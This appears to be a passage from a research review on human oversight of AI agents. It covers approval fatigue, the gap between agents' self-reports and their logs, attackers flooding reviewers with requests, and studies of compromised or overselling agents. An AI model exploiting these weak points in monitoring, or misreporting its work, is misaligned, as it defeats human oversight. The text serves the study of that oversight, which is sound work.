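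It is reasonable for people to adjust their attention to the risk, but they need to know where the risk is. In *The Oversight Fallacy*, a report for the research institute Data & Society, Passi and Singh (2026) describe a case from a biology laboratory in which the result didn't reveal the error. Researchers asked an agent to compare how fast fruit flies moved with a light on and with it off. The agent did not calculate an average for each fly and then average across the group, as it should have, but its final numbers were within the accepted range, so the work passed.

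When the researchers reviewed how the agent had reached those numbers, they found that it had used a single fly to represent the whole group. That fly happened to move at close to the average speed. Any statement that the result was an average across the group would have been false, which an accurate log could have revealed but a check of the numbers alone could not.

But reading such a log takes time. Passi and Singh cite a test in which five cooperating agents had to work out which two US presidents' birthplaces are farthest apart from west to east. The agents exchanged 90 messages totaling 7,230 words. Reading them at an ordinary speed would take about half an hour, much longer than most people would spend on such a question.

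Passi and Singh also argue that reliable agents can be harder to oversee than unreliable ones, because people become complacent. This affects how to interpret older experiments such as the one by Grunde-McLaughlin and colleagues, which used GPT-4o and GPT-5. Those models made many mistakes for participants to find. Current models make fewer, so their users get less practice at catching them.

The interviews explain why people don't check, but they can't show how often people miss errors, because people can't report errors they never noticed. The evidence is also not fully independent, because Samir Passi worked on both the developer interviews and the laboratory study, and most of the developers worked for the same company as the interviewers.

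### How many approvals a person can judge

People who approve an agent's actions one by one may get so many prompts that they stop paying close attention. Mitchell, Ghosh and Passi (2026) call this "approval fatigue" in *AI Agents Push Humans Out of the Loop*. *Oversight Has a Capacity* (2026) models the reviewer as someone who tires, and concludes that sending them too many requests can make an agent less safe. An attacker could exploit this by flooding the reviewer with requests.

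Hossain and colleagues' volunteers took a median of 33 seconds to answer a prompt with the consequence display. At that rate, someone who received 60 prompts a day would spend roughly 33 minutes answering them, compared with 16 minutes for the conventional prompt. The volunteers made only 12 decisions each, after two for practice, so the experiment can't show how they would have handled a sixtieth.

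The share of prompts that users accept is, by itself, almost useless for detecting fatigue in a real product. Hossain and colleagues' participants accepted 73% of requests with the conventional prompt and 55% with the consequence display. We can interpret those figures only because the researchers had made half of the requests harmful, so a perfect reviewer would have accepted 50%.

The share of an agent's requests that users approve doesn't show whether they read them, because nearly all requests may deserve approval in ordinary use. If one in 100 is harmful, a perfect reviewer approves 99% and someone who never reads them approves 100%, so a company that found a 99% approval rate couldn't tell which kind of user it had. A low rate wouldn't show careful reading either, since users may be refusing legitimate actions that they don't understand. To learn whether people are reading, the company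 would need to know which requests they should have refused, either by planting harmful ones or by investigating a sample afterwards.

The time a user spends on each prompt is somewhat more informative, because nobody can read a 30-line command in one second. But a long pause may only mean that the user was away from the screen.

### What no study has tested

The four main experiments differ in nearly everything that could affect whether people notice an error:

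| Study | What was wrong | What people saw | Who took part | Errors caught |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Grunde-McLaughlin and colleagues, second study | The agent's answer | Its record in one of three layouts | 12 technology employees | 39% to 65% |
| Dissanayake and colleagues | Code that passed its tests | The code, the tests and the agent's replies | 36 programmers | 39% |
| Hossain and colleagues | An action that broke the user's instruction | One of four approval displays | 80 volunteers | 45% to 76% |
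| Li and colleagues | An agent that an attacker had compromised | The agent's output and one of three warnings | 303 online participants | 9% to 25% |

The percentages measure different abilities, so they can't show which display is best. One difference between the studies probably explains much of the range. In the two with the highest rates, people were told to judge each answer or request, and at least half of the items were bad. Li and colleagues instead asked people to get a job done, which is how most people use agents, and questioned them only at the end.

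The studies also concentrate on what people see at a fixed moment. When people should get involved is a separate choice, and it matters because even an excellent log display can't help someone stop an email the agent has already sent. *Comparing Human Oversight Strategies for Computer-Use Agents* (Chen, Zhang and colleagues, 2026) examines oversight strategies for agents that operate a computer.

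None of the four experiments showed people a false self-report beside an accurate log and measured whether they noticed the conflict. The shopping cart experiment came close, but its log was false. Dissanayake and colleagues' participants had genuine test results. Hossain and colleagues provided an accurate log, but no account from the agent that contradicted it. Li and colleagues studied deception, but asked participants only whether the agent's output had seemed unusual.

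A conflict between report and log might be easier to notice than the errors in these experiments. In the date-bug session, a user who sees "pushed the branch" next to a log without a push can notice the conflict without understanding the code. This is more like checking a ballot against a written list, which is how voters caught the most errors. But the user has to look at the log, and the developers in the interviews preferred the plan and the summary.

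Each experiment also took place in a single session, so none can show what happens after weeks of accurate reports. This is hard to study because serious misreports are rare. Transluce found severe overselling in 1.8% of public coding sessions. At that rate, a developer who ran five sessions every working day for four weeks would encounter about two cases. To observe 200 such cases, researchers would need to follow more than 100 developers for a month, and they would have to find every case themselves to know which ones the developers had missed.

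Researchers could run the study with fewer people by planting false claims in reports. Participants would give general consent beforehand, and the researchers would correct the claims before anyone merged the code. One group would see only the report, another would see the log beside it, and a third would see the report with unsupported claims marked. The researchers would also have to count the true claims that people rejected, and record how often people opened the log in the first week and in the last. If Dissanayake and colleagues are right that suspicion fades after one correct task, people who read the log at first may stop within a week.
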